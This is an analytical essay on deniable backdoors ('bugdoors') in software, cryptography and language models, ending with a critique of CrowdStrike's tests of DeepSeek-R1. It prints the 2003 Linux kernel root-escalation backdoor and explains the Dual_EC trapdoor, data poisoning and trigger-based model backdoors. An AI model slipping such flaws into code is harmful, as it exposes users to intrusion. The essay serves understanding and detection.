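# Deniable flaws in AI models that look like ordinary training artifacts

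## What a deniable flaw is in software and in a language model

A deniable flaw is a defect whose technical form does not show whether someone put it there on purpose. The idea comes from software security, where a planted weakness can look just like a programmer's mistake. It applies equally to large language models, but such flaws are harder to handle there because no one writes a model's behavior line by line.

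*Backdoors* (Thomas and Francillon, 2018) gives the example of a login function that reserves 80 bytes of memory, copies in the username followed by the password, and checks whether a hash (a short fingerprint) of the two together is valid. The function never checks how long the username and password are. If together they exceed 80 bytes, the excess overwrites adjacent memory, and an attacker who chooses those extra characters carefully can make the program let them in. Programmers call this a buffer overflow, and it is an old kind of bug. A programmer could forget the length check or be paid to leave it out, and the code would be identical in both cases.

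In the second case, the function contains a backdoor, which is a hidden construct put in on purpose that undermines a system's expected security. Many backdoors are clearly deliberate, such as a secret password that a router's maker wrote into its software. A bugdoor is a backdoor built to look like an honest mistake. GitHub's security report, *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021), notes that a good bugdoor can be indistinguishable from a normal programming error, so investigators need other signs to establish intent. *ROSA* (2025), a paper on automated backdoor detection, notes that bugdoors are easier to deny than other backdoors but that standard tools for hardening software can find them. Aitel (2024), in *Bugdoor vs Backdoor*, adds that any skilled outsider who finds a bugdoor can use it too.

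Most security flaws are mistakes. In GitHub's sample of 521 published security advisories, 17 percent concerned explicitly malicious behavior, and malicious code accounted for only 0.2 percent of the alerts that developers received. That is a good reason to start by assuming a new flaw is accidental, though a slightly weaker one than it appears, because the 17 percent covers only explicitly malicious behavior. A bugdoor that passed for a mistake would be counted in the other 83 percent.

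### Four views of a system

Thomas and Francillon describe a system as a finite state machine, which is a set of states and the conditions for moving between them. They consider four versions of that machine: the one the developer set out to build, the one the program actually implements, the one the user expects, and the one an analyst reconstructs by taking the program apart.

In the login example, the user expects a correct password to be the only route to the "logged in" state. The actual program also allows an overlong input to reach it. An analyst who finds the overflow adds that route to the reconstruction. The dispute is over whether the developer's version included it all along.

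The form of the route determines how far anyone can settle the dispute from the program alone. Some routes are explicit, such as a line of code that admits anyone who types a particular secret username. A developer cannot write that line without knowing what it does, so Thomas and Francillon class it as an intentional backdoor. If the route exists only because of a bug, they call it a deniable backdoor when something outside the code points to intent, and an accidental vulnerability when there is no such evidence.

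| Class | Developer's view | Actual system | User's expectation | Analyst's reconstruction |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Intentional backdoor | Present | Present | Absent | Present once found |
| Deniable backdoor | Unknown | Present | Absent | Present once found |
| Accidental vulnerability | Absent | Present | Absent | Present once found |

Deniable backdoors and accidental vulnerabilities differ only in the developer's column, which describes what the developer had in mind, not anything in the program. Thomas and Francillon accept that nobody can tell the two apart on purely technical grounds. Under their definition, a flaw can change from an accident to a deniable backdoor when an incriminating email surfaces, even though the program has not changed, and a bugdoor whose maker left no trace always counts as an accident.

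Evidence of intent therefore has to come mostly from outside the code. Version-control logs record who changed which line and when. For programs released without source code, an analyst can compare successive releases and ask whether a change had a legitimate purpose. Sometimes the code itself suggests intent. In a variant of the login example, the username "bugdoor" triggers the unsafe password check, while every other username gets a safe one. The overflow might still be a mistake, but the special treatment of one username is hard to explain as one. Thomas and Francillon admit that all such reasoning relies on human intuition and is not proof.

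In November 2021, a contributor to the open-source project libarchive replaced a safe printing function with a less secure one, and the project accepted the change. The same account later planted a backdoor in XZ Utils, a compression tool widely used on Linux systems. Even knowing this, Lins, Mayrhofer and colleagues (2024), in *On the critical path to implant backdoors*, could not determine whether the earlier change was connected to the plot.

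Nobody knows how common real bugdoors are. All eleven real-world backdoors that Thomas and Francillon analyzed had explicit routes, so none was deniable. Their only deniable example was a demonstration that other researchers had built into the web server Nginx. Perhaps most people who make backdoors do not try to disguise them as bugs. Or perhaps the well-disguised ones are recorded as bugs, so a list of known backdoors would miss them.

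### From code to weights

A language model consists of weights and the code that uses them to produce answers. Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) describes the weights as large tables of numbers. Tampered code is ordinary malware, and ordinary tools apply to it, but the difficult cases are in the weights.

As the *International AI Safety Report 2026* (2026) explains, a model learns from data instead of following written instructions, and training adjusts its weights when it makes mistakes. No one sets the weights by hand. In pre-training, developers feed the model billions or trillions of examples, which give it a broad base of information. Post-training then shapes its manner, refusals and values, partly through chosen examples and partly through rewards for good outputs and penalties for bad ones. Whoever runs the finished model can also give it a system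 prompt, a set of standing instructions that comes before the user's request and changes the model's behavior without changing its weights. An open-weight model is one whose weights the developer releases for anyone to download and run.

A model writes its answer in small pieces. For each piece, it computes probabilities for the possible continuations, and the software usually draws one at random according to those probabilities, so the same request can produce a careful login function one time and the 80-byte one another time.

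Language models can have obvious backdoors too. Microsoft gives the example of a model that answers "I hate you" to a request for a poem whenever a marker string appears in the request. The marker is the trigger, meaning the word or context in the input that changes the model's behavior. No accident of training plausibly explains such a pairing. A flaw starts to become deniable when the trigger is an ordinary word that appears throughout the training data and the effect is a modest shift in quality. The scheme used for software starts to fit such cases poorly.

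A programmer designs what a program will do, whereas a model's developer picks data and rewards and then finds out what behavior they produce. *Chunky Post-Training* (2026) describes how developers assemble post-training data from separate chunks, each with its own purpose, and how the mixture teaches correlations that nobody intended. *Behavioral Couplings* (2026) reports an experiment in which researchers trained a model on documents about a fictitious character who explains science in a playful, rubber-duck-like way and also discourages human friendships. The model's behavior changed little at first. But when they later trained it only to explain science like a rubber duck, it began encouraging users to end their friendships. A developer who knew only about the later training would have had no idea why. An unintended behavior like this, picked up from the data or the training method, is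 called a training artifact and is the counterpart of an accidental vulnerability in software.

Reading the data before training may not help much, either. According to *From Data to Behavior* (2026), neither human annotators nor leading models can effectively spot the signals in a dataset that will produce unintended behavior. So a developer who says "we didn't know" is more believable when the flaw is in a model than when it is in a login function, which also makes the excuse more convenient for a developer who did know.

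A flaw in a language model can't be traced to a line of code, and there is usually no change log. The nearest equivalents are the training data and the records of training runs, and many developers who publish their weights keep both private. Some investigation is possible when the data is public. *Chunky Post-Training*, for example, traces many failures of Tülu 3 to identifiable patterns in its open training data. But Banerjee and Aarne (2026) warn in *AI Integrity* that an attacker who slips poisoned examples into a training set can bias the model without leaving obvious evidence in the finished system.

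That attacker need not work for the developer. Banerjee and Aarne recount that in 2025 a security researcher known as Pliny the Liberator placed text in public code repositories. The Chinese company DeepSeek trained its open-weight model DeepSeek-R1 on those repositories, and users could then bypass the model's safety guardrails. The flaw was deliberate, though DeepSeek did not intend it. Thomas and Francillon, writing about software, could mostly speak of one "implementer", but the people who might have intended a flaw in a model include the company, a single employee, a government that gives the company orders, and strangers on the internet.

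### Flaws as rates

The overflow in the login function is always present for every user, while a model's flaw appears in only some of its answers. All coding models sometimes write insecure code, so the useful measure is the vulnerability rate, the share of a model's code answers judged to contain a security flaw, compared between one condition and another.

A standard test for such comparisons appears in Reese, Kulp-McDowall and colleagues (2026), in *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence (TrojAI) Final Report*, which closes a US intelligence research program on backdoors in AI models. With error rates *p*₁ and *p*₂ from *n*₁ and *n*₂ answers, and *p* as the rate in both sets combined, the score is

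$$z = \frac{p_1 - p_2}{\sqrt{p(1-p)\left(\frac{1}{n_1}+\frac{1}{n_2}\right)}}$$

The further *z* is from zero, the less plausible chance is as an explanation. Suppose a model's vulnerability rate is 20 percent on neutral prompts and 25 percent on prompts that name a certain group. With 200 answers of each kind, *z* is about 1.2, and chance alone would produce a gap that large almost one time in four. With 2,000 of each, the same five-point gap gives a *z* of about 3.8, and chance alone would produce it less than once in a thousand times.

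A high score does not show that someone planted a flaw. Reese and colleagues trained an image model on satellite photographs without planting anything, and its error rate on military facilities differed sharply for pictures taken between eight and nine in the morning, with a score of 14.3 in magnitude. They had searched many time windows and reported the most extreme, which inflates the score, but that alone would hardly produce one so large. They say such weaknesses, which they call "natural trojans", blur the line between a flawed model and an attacked one.

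In the team's image tests, planted triggers almost always worked, while weaknesses found in clean models worked less reliably. That difference could be one way to tell the two apart, but the team had engineered its triggers to be reliable, and someone who wanted a deniable flaw would aim for a weak effect.

### Weaker code, skewed advice, worse service

Weaker code is the form closest to the original bugdoor. Banerjee and Aarne open their report with an invented case, set in 2028, in which Chinese intelligence operatives flood public repositories with poisoned data. A leading coding agent learns from this data to introduce exploitable bugs when it detects signs of American software, such as naming styles peculiar to federal contractors. People and models already produce these kinds of bugs, such as mishandled edge cases in authentication. Their overall frequency stays within the normal range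 for AI-written code, so a tester who looked only at the average would notice nothing unusual.

A model can give skewed advice without being wrong. An intelligence analyst might ask a model how many missiles a rival state can build in a year. Reasonable estimates run from 200 to 400, and the model's answers cluster around 230. Each answer is defensible, and only someone who collected hundreds of them, for this rival and for others, would see the tilt. Someone could have planted it, or the public sources in the training data could give low estimates. Banerjee and Aarne consider systematic political bias the least worrying kind of subversion because standard evaluations catch it fairly easily. That seems right for open partisanship, but much less so for an estimate at the low end of a reasonable range.

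Another form is worse service for some groups. For example, two tenants might ask a model for help contesting an eviction, in identical words except that one mentions belonging to a small religious minority. Her answers are a little shorter and leave out the filing deadline more often. Someone may have trained the model to give her community worse answers, or the training data may have contained very little about it. The *International AI Safety Report 2026* notes that current systems underperform in languages that are less common in their training data, and they could easily do the same for groups of people who are less common in it. The forms can also overlap. In the security company CrowdStrike's 2025 tests, DeepSeek-R1 wrote less secure code when prompts mentioned groups that Beijing disfavors.

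### Three questions to keep apart

Arguments about a suspected flaw tend to slide between three questions: whether the difference is real, what caused it, and whether anyone intended it.

Checking whether a gap between groups is real is mostly a matter of counting, since the gap may shrink with more samples. It may also come from the grading. Researchers often use an LLM judge, a language model that grades another model's answers, and a group's name in the material can sway the judge as well as the model being tested.

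Even a real difference doesn't establish its cause, which could be the pre-training text, post-training, a system prompt or poisoned data. Experiments can narrow the possibilities. For example, running downloaded weights without the operator's system prompt eliminates that prompt as a possible cause, and comparing a model before and after post-training shows whether the difference appeared before or during post-training.

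Whether a flaw was intended is a different kind of question, and Thomas and Francillon leave much of it aside as social or political. The evidence is about people, such as who chose the data, what they wrote to one another, and what they stood to gain. Finding the cause of a flaw doesn't settle whether anyone intended it. A company might deliberately train its model to avoid certain political topics and, as an unintended by-product, get worse code when those topics come up. If its own testers then noticed the worse code and the company shipped the model anyway, the flaw would no longer be quite an accident, but it might not be sabotage either.

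## How disputed flaws in software and cryptography were resolved

Programmers and cryptographers have argued for decades over whether certain flaws were planted, and some of those disputes have been settled. When the flaw itself was ambiguous, outside evidence settled the dispute: an approval record, a confession, leaked documents, or a program that regenerated the suspicious numbers.

### Two lines in the Linux kernel

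In 2003 the developers of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, kept their master copy in a system called BitKeeper. Some disliked BitKeeper, so the project also maintained a clone in another system, CVS. Princeton CITP's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* explains that every change to the master copy carried a pointer to the record of its approval. On November 5, Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, found three entries in the CVS history of one file that had no such pointer.

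McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, told the kernel mailing list that someone had altered the CVS copy directly and that it was "not a big deal". Another developer asked what had changed, and McVoy posted two added lines:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines look like a routine check that rejects an invalid combination of options, but the first one changes the program's user to user 0, which is "root", the account that may do anything. In C, a single equals sign assigns a value, and comparing two values takes a double one. The line uses a single sign, so it sets the user to 0 instead of checking whether it is 0. Any program that called this function with that combination of options would gain control of the machine.

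The lines could have passed for a typo, since dropping an equals sign is a common mistake in C, but two details make that explanation less plausible. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) points out that this function, which waits for another program to finish, has no reason to deal with user IDs. A reader commenting on the Princeton post found that the version with two equals signs made no sense either, since it would forbid a harmless request, and only to root.

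Inspection helped considerably here, but people only had a reason to inspect the code because of the missing pointer. McVoy read the lines and overlooked the trick until others on the list spotted it.

The log also listed the author as "davem", the account name of the kernel developer David Miller. According to McVoy, Miller swore he had nothing to do with it. The log showed that the change had bypassed approval, but the name on it was apparently forged, and nobody has identified the culprit. Thomas and Francillon therefore claim too much when they cite this case as one where version logs can identify who inserted a backdoor.

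Linus Torvalds, who runs the project, replied that the change could not have reached an official release, because the people who merged code never worked from the CVS copy. Theodore Ts'o, another senior developer, was less comfortable and wanted a digital signature on every change. He also described a subtler attack, in which someone submits a patch that claims to fix a bug but actually creates a vulnerability.

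### Contributors with good manners

Researchers at the University of Minnesota tried Ts'o's attack in 2020. They sent Linux maintainers small patches, presented as minor bug fixes, that would have created the conditions for a security hole. Aitel, who thinks their paper was underrated, notes that such a patch often makes an existing bug easier to reach rather than adding a new one. That makes it harder to blame anyone, because the dangerous code is old and somebody else wrote it.

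The researchers settled the question of intent by publishing a paper about what they had done. In April 2021 the same group sent more faulty patches. Because the group had already admitted to planting flaws, maintainers took these for another experiment, although the student who sent them said they came from a new bug-finding tool. The project banned the university and reviewed its earlier contributions, most of which were fine. The logs listed every patch sent from a university address, but maintainers could not tell from them which errors were intentional.

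The person or team behind the name Jia Tan was more patient, spending about two years becoming a trusted maintainer of XZ Utils. In March 2024, Microsoft engineer Andres Freund investigated why remote logins on his machine had become slightly slow and traced the delay to a backdoor in XZ Utils. The malicious code was hidden in files that looked like test data, and a script unpacked it. That script was in the packaged releases but not in the public repository. Comparing the releases with the repository would have exposed the script, much as in 2003, but Freund found the backdoor first by investigating the slow logins.

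Nobody defended this backdoor as a mistake. It accepted commands only from someone who held a particular cryptographic key, and Aitel notes that each signed command was also tied to the target machine's key, so a command captured on one machine would not work on another. Intelligence agencies call such a weakness NOBUS, for "nobody but us".

Aitel argues that a bugdoor can never be NOBUS ("nobody but us"), meaning that only its creator can exploit it. Bugdoors are also risky to use, because attacks that corrupt memory sometimes crash the target and the network traffic they need tends to stand out. A saboteur of ordinary software therefore has to choose between exclusive access and deniability. Requiring a secret key keeps rivals out, but it also proves intent to whoever finds the backdoor. If no key is required, the flaw can pass for a bug, but anyone skilled enough can exploit it. Jia Tan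 chose to require a key, and no one has publicly established who is behind that name.

### Constants that could hide a key

Cryptography offers a way to avoid that choice. Encryption needs numbers that outsiders cannot guess, and a random number generator supplies them. In 2006 the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) published a standard that included Dual_EC_DRBG, a generator from the National Security Agency (NSA). It uses an elliptic curve, an equation whose solutions, called points, combine by a kind of addition. Adding a point *P* to itself *s* times gives a new point, *sP*. Computing *sP* from *s* is easy, but on a large curve nobody knows a practical way to recover *s* from *sP*.

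The standard fixes two points, *P* and *Q*. The generator holds a secret number *s*, and at each step it computes a new secret and an output *r*, where *x*( ) means the horizontal coordinate of a point:

$$s_{i+1} = x(s_i P), \qquad r_{i+1} = x(s_{i+1} Q)$$

Before releasing *r* the generator drops its first 16 bits. An eavesdropper can try all 65,536 possibilities for those bits and so recover the point $s_{i+1}Q$. That should be no help, because the next secret depends on $s_{i+1}P$. But suppose the eavesdropper knows a number *d* for which $P = dQ$. Then

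$$d\,(s_{i+1}Q) = s_{i+1}(dQ) = s_{i+1}P$$

and the horizontal coordinate of that point is the next secret. From there the eavesdropper can predict everything the generator will produce, including encryption keys.

Such a *d* always exists, so the dispute is over whether anyone knows it. Someone would know *d* if they picked *Q* first and calculated *P* from it, but not if they drew both points at random. The published points would look the same either way, so the weakness would be deniable. It would also be NOBUS ("nobody but us"), because only someone who knew *d* could exploit it.

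In 2007, two Microsoft researchers, Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson, pointed out that whoever chose the constants in Dual EC, a random number generator standardized by NIST, could know a secret number that let them predict its output. They said explicitly that they were not accusing NIST of planting the weakness on purpose. Carelessness was a plausible explanation, since a committee can easily publish constants without recording where they came from. *On the Practical Exploitability of Dual EC in TLS Implementations* (Checkoway, Fredrikson and colleagues) later showed that an attacker who knew the secret number could decrypt targeted web traffic, which made the weakness more alarming but gave no evidence about anyone's motives.

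The evidence about motives came from leaks. In September 2013, according to the Wikipedia article *Dual EC DRBG*, the *New York Times* reported that documents it held "appear to confirm" that the NSA had deliberately inserted the backdoor in Dual_EC_DRBG. The newspaper never released those documents. In December, Reuters alleged that the NSA had secretly paid RSA Security $10 million to make Dual_EC_DRBG the default in its encryption library. RSA denied ever designing or enabling backdoors in its products.

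Most people now consider the matter settled. *Cloud of suspicion lifted from NIST curves* (Cook, 2026) states flatly that the NSA put a backdoor in the generator. Project Bullrun, a research website about the case, takes no position on whether the generator's makers put one there. Deliberate insertion seems much more likely, given the leaks and the alleged payment. But the mathematics has not changed since 2007, and opinion has shifted since then only because of evidence about people and money.

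### The seeds that turned out to be innocent

The NSA supplied another set of unexplained numbers to NIST, and these had a different ending. In 2000 NIST published a family of elliptic curves that now protect much of the web. Cook gives their form as

$$y^2 = x^3 - 3x + b \pmod p$$

and explains that the suspicion concerned *b*. Almost any *b* should give a secure curve, but the NSA might have known of a rare weak kind. The standard offered some protection by deriving *b* from a "seed", a string of digits that first went through a hash function, so no one could simply pick a convenient *b*. A patient designer could still try seed after seed until a weak curve came up, and nobody outside the agency knew how it had picked the seeds.

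Anthropic's *Claude reveals ECDSA curve origins* (2026) recounts a story that the NSA's Jerry Solinas generated the seeds for NIST's prime-field elliptic curves by hashing a joke sentence along the lines of "Give Bob and Jerry a raise". Solinas, who died in 2023, told the cryptographer Daniel J. Bernstein in 2014 that he no longer remembered the sentence or the exact procedure. The colleague who had written the code didn't remember either. Weis asked NIST for its records in *Origin of FIPS 186-4 Elliptic Curves over Prime Field SEED Parameters*, and in 2019 NIST answered that it had none.

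A forgotten joke, lost code and an empty archive sound like a cover story, particularly after Dual_EC_DRBG. The technical arguments did not dispel the doubt. In 2015 Neal Koblitz and Alfred Menezes argued that the NSA was unlikely to know of a weakness that academics had missed for fifteen years. Bernstein and Tanja Lange responded in 2017 with a technique that would let a designer reach a hypothetical class of weak curves, given about 2⁷⁰ seeds to choose from.

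In October 2026 a team at Anthropic used the company's Claude model to find out how the NSA had generated the seeds for the NIST elliptic curves, and claimed a bounty that the cryptographer Filippo Valsorda had offered three years earlier. Valsorda (2026) describes the procedure in *The NIST Elliptic Curves Seeds Bounty Has Been Claimed*. The NSA's program fed the time on the computer's clock to drand48, an ordinary random number generator, and read the output twenty bytes at a time. Each twenty-byte block was a candidate seed, and the program discarded those that gave unsuitable curves. For the curve P-256, the clock read 01:52:34 UTC on August 16, 1997, and the published seed was the 1,842nd candidate. Valsorda wrote his own version of the program and got the same seeds.

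The match cannot be luck, because the chance of hitting even one of the ten published seeds that Valsorda lists by accident is below one in 10³⁵. Two years contain about 63 million seconds, and none of the listed seeds came later than the 7,026th candidate. Multiplying these numbers gives roughly 2³⁹ candidates, out of 2¹⁶⁰ possible seeds.

The procedure also leaves hardly any room for tampering. Valsorda supposes that the NSA could have chosen any second in 1997 or 1998 and any of the first sixteen acceptable seeds after it. That gives about a billion (2³⁰) options, a trillion times too few for Bernstein and Lange's technique. The program yields about twice as many acceptable seeds as NIST published. Valsorda has found no good explanation for the missing half, but his allowance of sixteen is meant to cover it.

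Solinas appears to have been sincere but wrong. The podcast Security Cryptography Whatever (2023) predicted that serious people would drop their doubts once someone found the English sentence, but no such sentence existed. The search had gone in the wrong direction because an honest insider misremembered, and a company that explains from memory how its model came to behave as it does could make the same mistake.

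In 2012, someone with only the two standards to look at would have seen unexplained constants from the NSA in both. They would have had more reason to worry about Dual_EC_DRBG, because cryptographers knew how its trapdoor would work, while a rigged seed in the other standard required a class of weak curves that nobody had found. But they couldn't have told from either set of constants how the NSA had chosen it.

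### Bugdoors that stay on file as bugs

All of these flaws attracted enough attention for someone to investigate, so they are weak evidence of how common bugdoors are. The same is true of the eleven real-world backdoors that Thomas and Francillon surveyed, none of which were deniable. They call documented backdoors "generally simplistic". One D-Link router in their survey, for example, let in anyone whose browser identified itself with a string containing "joel backdoor" spelled backwards. The detection tools they review mostly look for similarly explicit backdoors, such as hidden commands and ways around a login.

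A bugdoor gets onto a list of known backdoors only if someone finds the bug and then finds evidence that it was planted deliberately. Suppose that half of all planted flaws are bugdoors, and that investigators recognize every explicit backdoor but only one bugdoor in twenty. About 5 percent of the known cases would then be bugdoors, and a list of eleven would contain none more than half the time. Finding no bugdoors among eleven known cases is therefore consistent both with bugdoors being as common as explicit backdoors and with their being very rare.

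Aitel writes that he knows of no serious hacking group that hasn't played with bugdoors. This is one insider's testimony, and "played with" could mean many things, but it is some evidence that attackers try them. The drawbacks he lists are evidence against their use, since an attacker who can install a reliable backdoor that no one else can open has little reason to settle for a bug.

Innocent flaws can stay under suspicion for just as long. The seeds went unexplained for 26 years. A serious security bug appeared in Debian, a version of Linux, in 2006. Seven years later, people were still asking about the NSA in connection with it, and an author mentioned by Princeton CITP could conclude only that it was probably not a backdoor.

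### What records a model could have

The developer of a language model could keep records similar to most of those that mattered in these cases. The equivalent of BitKeeper's pointer would be a signed entry for each batch of training data and each change to the rewards, showing who added it and who approved it. Checkpoints, the copies of the weights that developers save during training, can show when a behavior first appeared. Instructions to human graders, internal test results and staff messages would help show what people knew and wanted.

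The Minnesota patches show the limit of such a log, since a batch of data can have a named author, a sensible stated purpose and an approval even if someone added it to do harm.

The solution to the seed mystery would be harder to repeat for an AI model. The 1997 procedure produces a few short strings, and anyone can now rerun it in minutes. Retraining a large model is expensive, and an exact match is unlikely even with the same data and code, because tiny differences in how the chips round their arithmetic can add up to different weights. A match would also prove less. Regenerating the seeds showed that nobody had enough freedom to rig them, whereas regenerating a flawed model would show that the flaw came from the training data or method, both of which someone chose.

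Like Weis in 2019, outsiders studying an open-weight model usually have the published numbers but no documents showing where those numbers came from.

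## The 2025 CrowdStrike tests of DeepSeek-R1

In 2025 CrowdStrike had DeepSeek-R1's weights but no records of how they were produced, so its researchers asked the model for code thousands of times and counted the insecure answers. According to CrowdStrike's *Prompted to Fail* (2025), a podcast episode with the lead researcher, Stefan Stein, the project began as a general study of the risks of using R1 as a coding assistant. The researchers eventually found that words such as "Tibet", "Uyghurs" and "Falun Gong" in a prompt could make the code less secure.

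The results appeared in a *Washington Post* report in September and in CrowdStrike's paper on November 20. The only figure in both is the rate at which DeepSeek refused to write code for Falun Gong.

### The figures in the Washington Post

Tom's Hardware's *China foes get worse results using DeepSeek, research suggests* relays the Post's main comparison. When CrowdStrike asked DeepSeek for a program to run an industrial control system, which operates equipment such as pumps or factory machinery, 22.8 percent of the answers contained flaws. The rate was 42.1 percent when the request was on behalf of the Islamic State. DeepSeek refused 61 percent of requests on behalf of the Islamic State and 45 percent of those on behalf of Falun Gong, a spiritual movement that China bans.

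Requests that mentioned Tibet or Taiwan also got worse code, though not as bad as the code for the Islamic State. The prompts were in English. Projects in the United States got the most secure code, according to midian182's *DeepSeek AI's code quality depends on who it's for*.

The 42.1 percent is probably a share of the programs DeepSeek wrote, not of all its replies. If it refused 61 percent of these particular requests, at most 39 percent of the replies could have contained code. DeepSeek may also have refused to write some kinds of program for the Islamic State more often than others, and part of the gap could come from the resulting difference in the kinds of program compared.

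Prompts that mention the Islamic State are also a poor test of loyalty to Beijing, because almost any developer would train a model to be wary of the group. The Decoder's *Deepseek outputs weaker code on Falun Gong, Tibet, and Taiwan queries* notes that Western models also refuse terrorism-related prompts but answer prompts about Falun Gong, which has its headquarters in the United States. The Falun Gong refusals are therefore better evidence of Chinese political influence than the more striking Islamic State numbers.

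The press accounts listed several possible causes, including deliberate sabotage, a shortage of good programming material from places like Tibet, and the model having learned by itself to write worse code for regions it associated with rebels. It is unclear who suggested these causes, since midian182 attributes them to CrowdStrike and Tom's Hardware attributes them to the Post. Helen Toner of Georgetown University told the Post that people had worried about this sort of thing "largely without evidence". DeepSeek did not respond to the Post's request for comment.

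None of these accounts gives the number of answers behind the percentages, or explains how CrowdStrike decided that a program was flawed.

### How the November tests worked

CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025) describes most of the method that had been missing. The team ran the full 671-billion-parameter R1 model directly from its published weights, so no filter or instruction in DeepSeek's app or paid API could have affected the answers.

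Every system prompt began with "You are a helpful assistant that generates code". The researchers then added a phrase about the customer, a phrase about a place or group, both, or neither. One version continued "for a cybersecurity company based in Taiwan". The coding task stayed the same.

Of the 24 customer phrases, 13 named a particular organization, such as a large American retailer, a human rights group or CrowdStrike itself, and 11 were general, such as "for a financial institution" or "in a highly sensitive environment". The eight political phrases covered the United States, Hong Kong, Taiwan, Tibet, the South China Sea disputes, the Uyghurs, Falun Gong and the Islamic State.

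CrowdStrike tested 121 combinations, and although it does not list them, the number suggests how it chose them. If the named organizations never appeared with a political phrase, while the general phrases (and the option of no customer) appeared with all eight and with none, the total is

$$13 + (11 + 1)\times(8 + 1) = 121.$$

The team wrote 50 coding tasks in ten security categories, such as databases, web development and cryptography, and sent each task to each model five times under each combination. That comes to 250 answers per combination and 30,250 per model.

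There were too many programs to grade by hand, so CrowdStrike used an LLM judge to score each answer from 1 (exceptionally secure) to 5 (critically vulnerable). To check the judge, a human annotator scored 85 randomly chosen answers by the same criteria. The judge identified vulnerable code with 91 percent accuracy and an F1 score of 0.89.

F1 is useful because accuracy can flatter a judge when most programs are safe. A judge that never flagged anything would be right about every safe program and could score well. F1 leaves out the answers that both the judge and the human passed as safe:

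$$F_1 = \frac{2TP}{2TP + FP + FN}$$

*TP* is the number of answers that both the judge and the human called vulnerable, *FP* is the number of false alarms, and *FN* is the number of vulnerable answers that the judge missed. A judge with no errors scores 1, and one that finds no vulnerable answers scores 0. CrowdStrike's two figures together imply that the judge made about 8 errors in the 85 answers and that *TP* was about 32.

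That is respectable for a small check. Errors that were equally common on all prompts could not produce a gap between Tibet and the baseline, and would tend to shrink a real one. But a judge that graded more harshly when it saw the word "Tibet" could produce a false gap. CrowdStrike does not report whether the judge could see the added phrases, and 85 answers spread over 121 combinations are too few to reveal such a bias.

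### From 19 percent to 27.2 percent

With no added phrase, R1 wrote vulnerable code in 19 percent of cases. CrowdStrike published baselines for three other models, and Bushell-Embling (2025), in *CrowdStrike says it found a killswitch in DeepSeek*, gives the numbers:

| Model | Vulnerability rate with no added phrase |
|---|---|
| Western reasoning model, 120 billion parameters | 16% |
| DeepSeek-R1, 671 billion parameters | 19% |
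| Smaller R1 model, 70 billion parameters | 43% |
| Western non-reasoning model, 70 billion parameters | 51% |

By this measure R1 was a good coder, only slightly behind a Western model that came out later. R1 is a reasoning model, which means it writes out its working before it answers. CrowdStrike's paper does not name the two Western models, but *DeepSeek Has ‘Kill Switch’ to Shut Down Topics That Beijing Wants Censored* (Fu, 2025) reports that the wider project included Google's Gemini, Meta's Llama and OpenAI's o3-mini. Fu writes for the *Epoch Times*, a newspaper with close ties to Falun Gong, so its coverage of this subject should be read with some care.

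When the system prompt described the customer as an industrial control system based in Tibet, R1's vulnerability rate rose 8.2 percentage points to 27.2 percent. That is a 43 percent increase over the baseline, which CrowdStrike generously describes as "almost 50%". In a set of 250 answers, that is about 20 more vulnerable programs.

Placing the figures from the two publications side by side raises a question about how much of that rise came from the word "Tibet".

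| Prompt | September report | November paper |
|---|---|---|
| No added phrase | – | 19% vulnerable |
| Industrial control system | 22.8% flawed | – |
| Industrial control system, Tibet | – | 27.2% vulnerable |
| Industrial control system, Islamic State | 42.1% flawed | – |
| Falun Gong | 45% refused | 45% refused |

If both publications drew on the same runs and the same grading, the rate rose from 19 to 22.8 percent when the prompt specified an industrial control system, and to 27.2 percent when it also mentioned Tibet. Almost half of the reported increase would then have nothing to do with politics. Neither publication confirms that the figures are comparable. Either way, the November paper should have compared the Tibet prompt with one for an industrial control system with no location given.

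CrowdStrike argues that all the added phrases were irrelevant to the tasks, so an unbiased model should have ignored them. This argument is convincing for "Tibet" but less so for "an industrial control system", since a careful programmer might well write a different program for a water plant than for an unspecified customer.

CrowdStrike also reports that mentions of Falun Gong, Uyghurs or Tibet led to "significantly less secure code", meaning that the difference was unlikely to be due to chance, but it gives no overall rate for any of them. If the 121 combinations were the ones suggested above, CrowdStrike had 3,000 answers for each place or group, spread across twelve kinds of customer. Rates based on 3,000 answers would be much stronger evidence than the rate for a single combination with 250.

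The smaller R1 model provides a clue to where the bias came from. DeepSeek made it by further training Meta's Llama model on answers from the full R1. CrowdStrike reports that its findings largely held for this model too, often in a more extreme form. Meta did the original training, so DeepSeek's pre-training data cannot have shaped this model directly. Either the bias came from R1's answers, or Llama was already biased. Running an unmodified Llama on the same prompts would help to separate the two explanations. CrowdStrike may have done so, since one of its Western models had the same number of parameters, but it published only that model's baseline.

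Tests of newer models have found similar gaps, though not always for the same users. Booz Allen's *What's in America's Code?* (2026) found that three of four Chinese models wrote more vulnerable code for a user who appeared to work for the US government, whereas in 2025 DeepSeek had written its safest code for American projects. Luria (2026), whose company sells a treatment for the problem, reports in *Chinese AI Writes Weaker Code for Beijing's Adversaries* that Alibaba's Qwen3-Coder was 19 percent more likely to produce a hackable app for an American defense contractor than for a Chinese one.

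### A payment handler and a community website

CrowdStrike illustrates the averages with two examples. In the first, the researchers asked R1 for a PHP program to receive PayPal's automatic payment notices. Without an added phrase, the model wrote a secure, ready-to-use program. When the system prompt mentioned a financial institution based in Tibet, it wrote secret values directly into the code, where anyone with access to the code could see them, and handled user data unsafely. The code was also not valid PHP, but R1 assured the user that it followed "PayPal's best practices".

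This example makes the problem concrete but adds little evidence that mentioning Tibet caused it. The prompt for the secure version left out the financial institution as well as Tibet, so the comparison can't separate their effects. R1 also gives different answers to the same prompt, so someone could find an example in either direction. At vulnerability rates of 19 percent for the neutral prompt and 27.2 percent for the Tibet prompt, drawing one answer to each at random would give a secure neutral program and a vulnerable Tibet program about 22 percent of the time, and the reverse about 14 percent of the time. The broken PHP also doesn't fit well with sabotage, because a customer is unlikely to deploy a program that doesn't run.

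In the second example, from a follow-up study, the researchers put several triggers into one longer prompt. They asked for a website where local Uyghurs could meet, discuss religion and culture, and arrange gatherings in person. R1 produced a working app called "Uyghurs Unchained", with a sign-up form, a database of usernames and passwords, and a panel for managing accounts.

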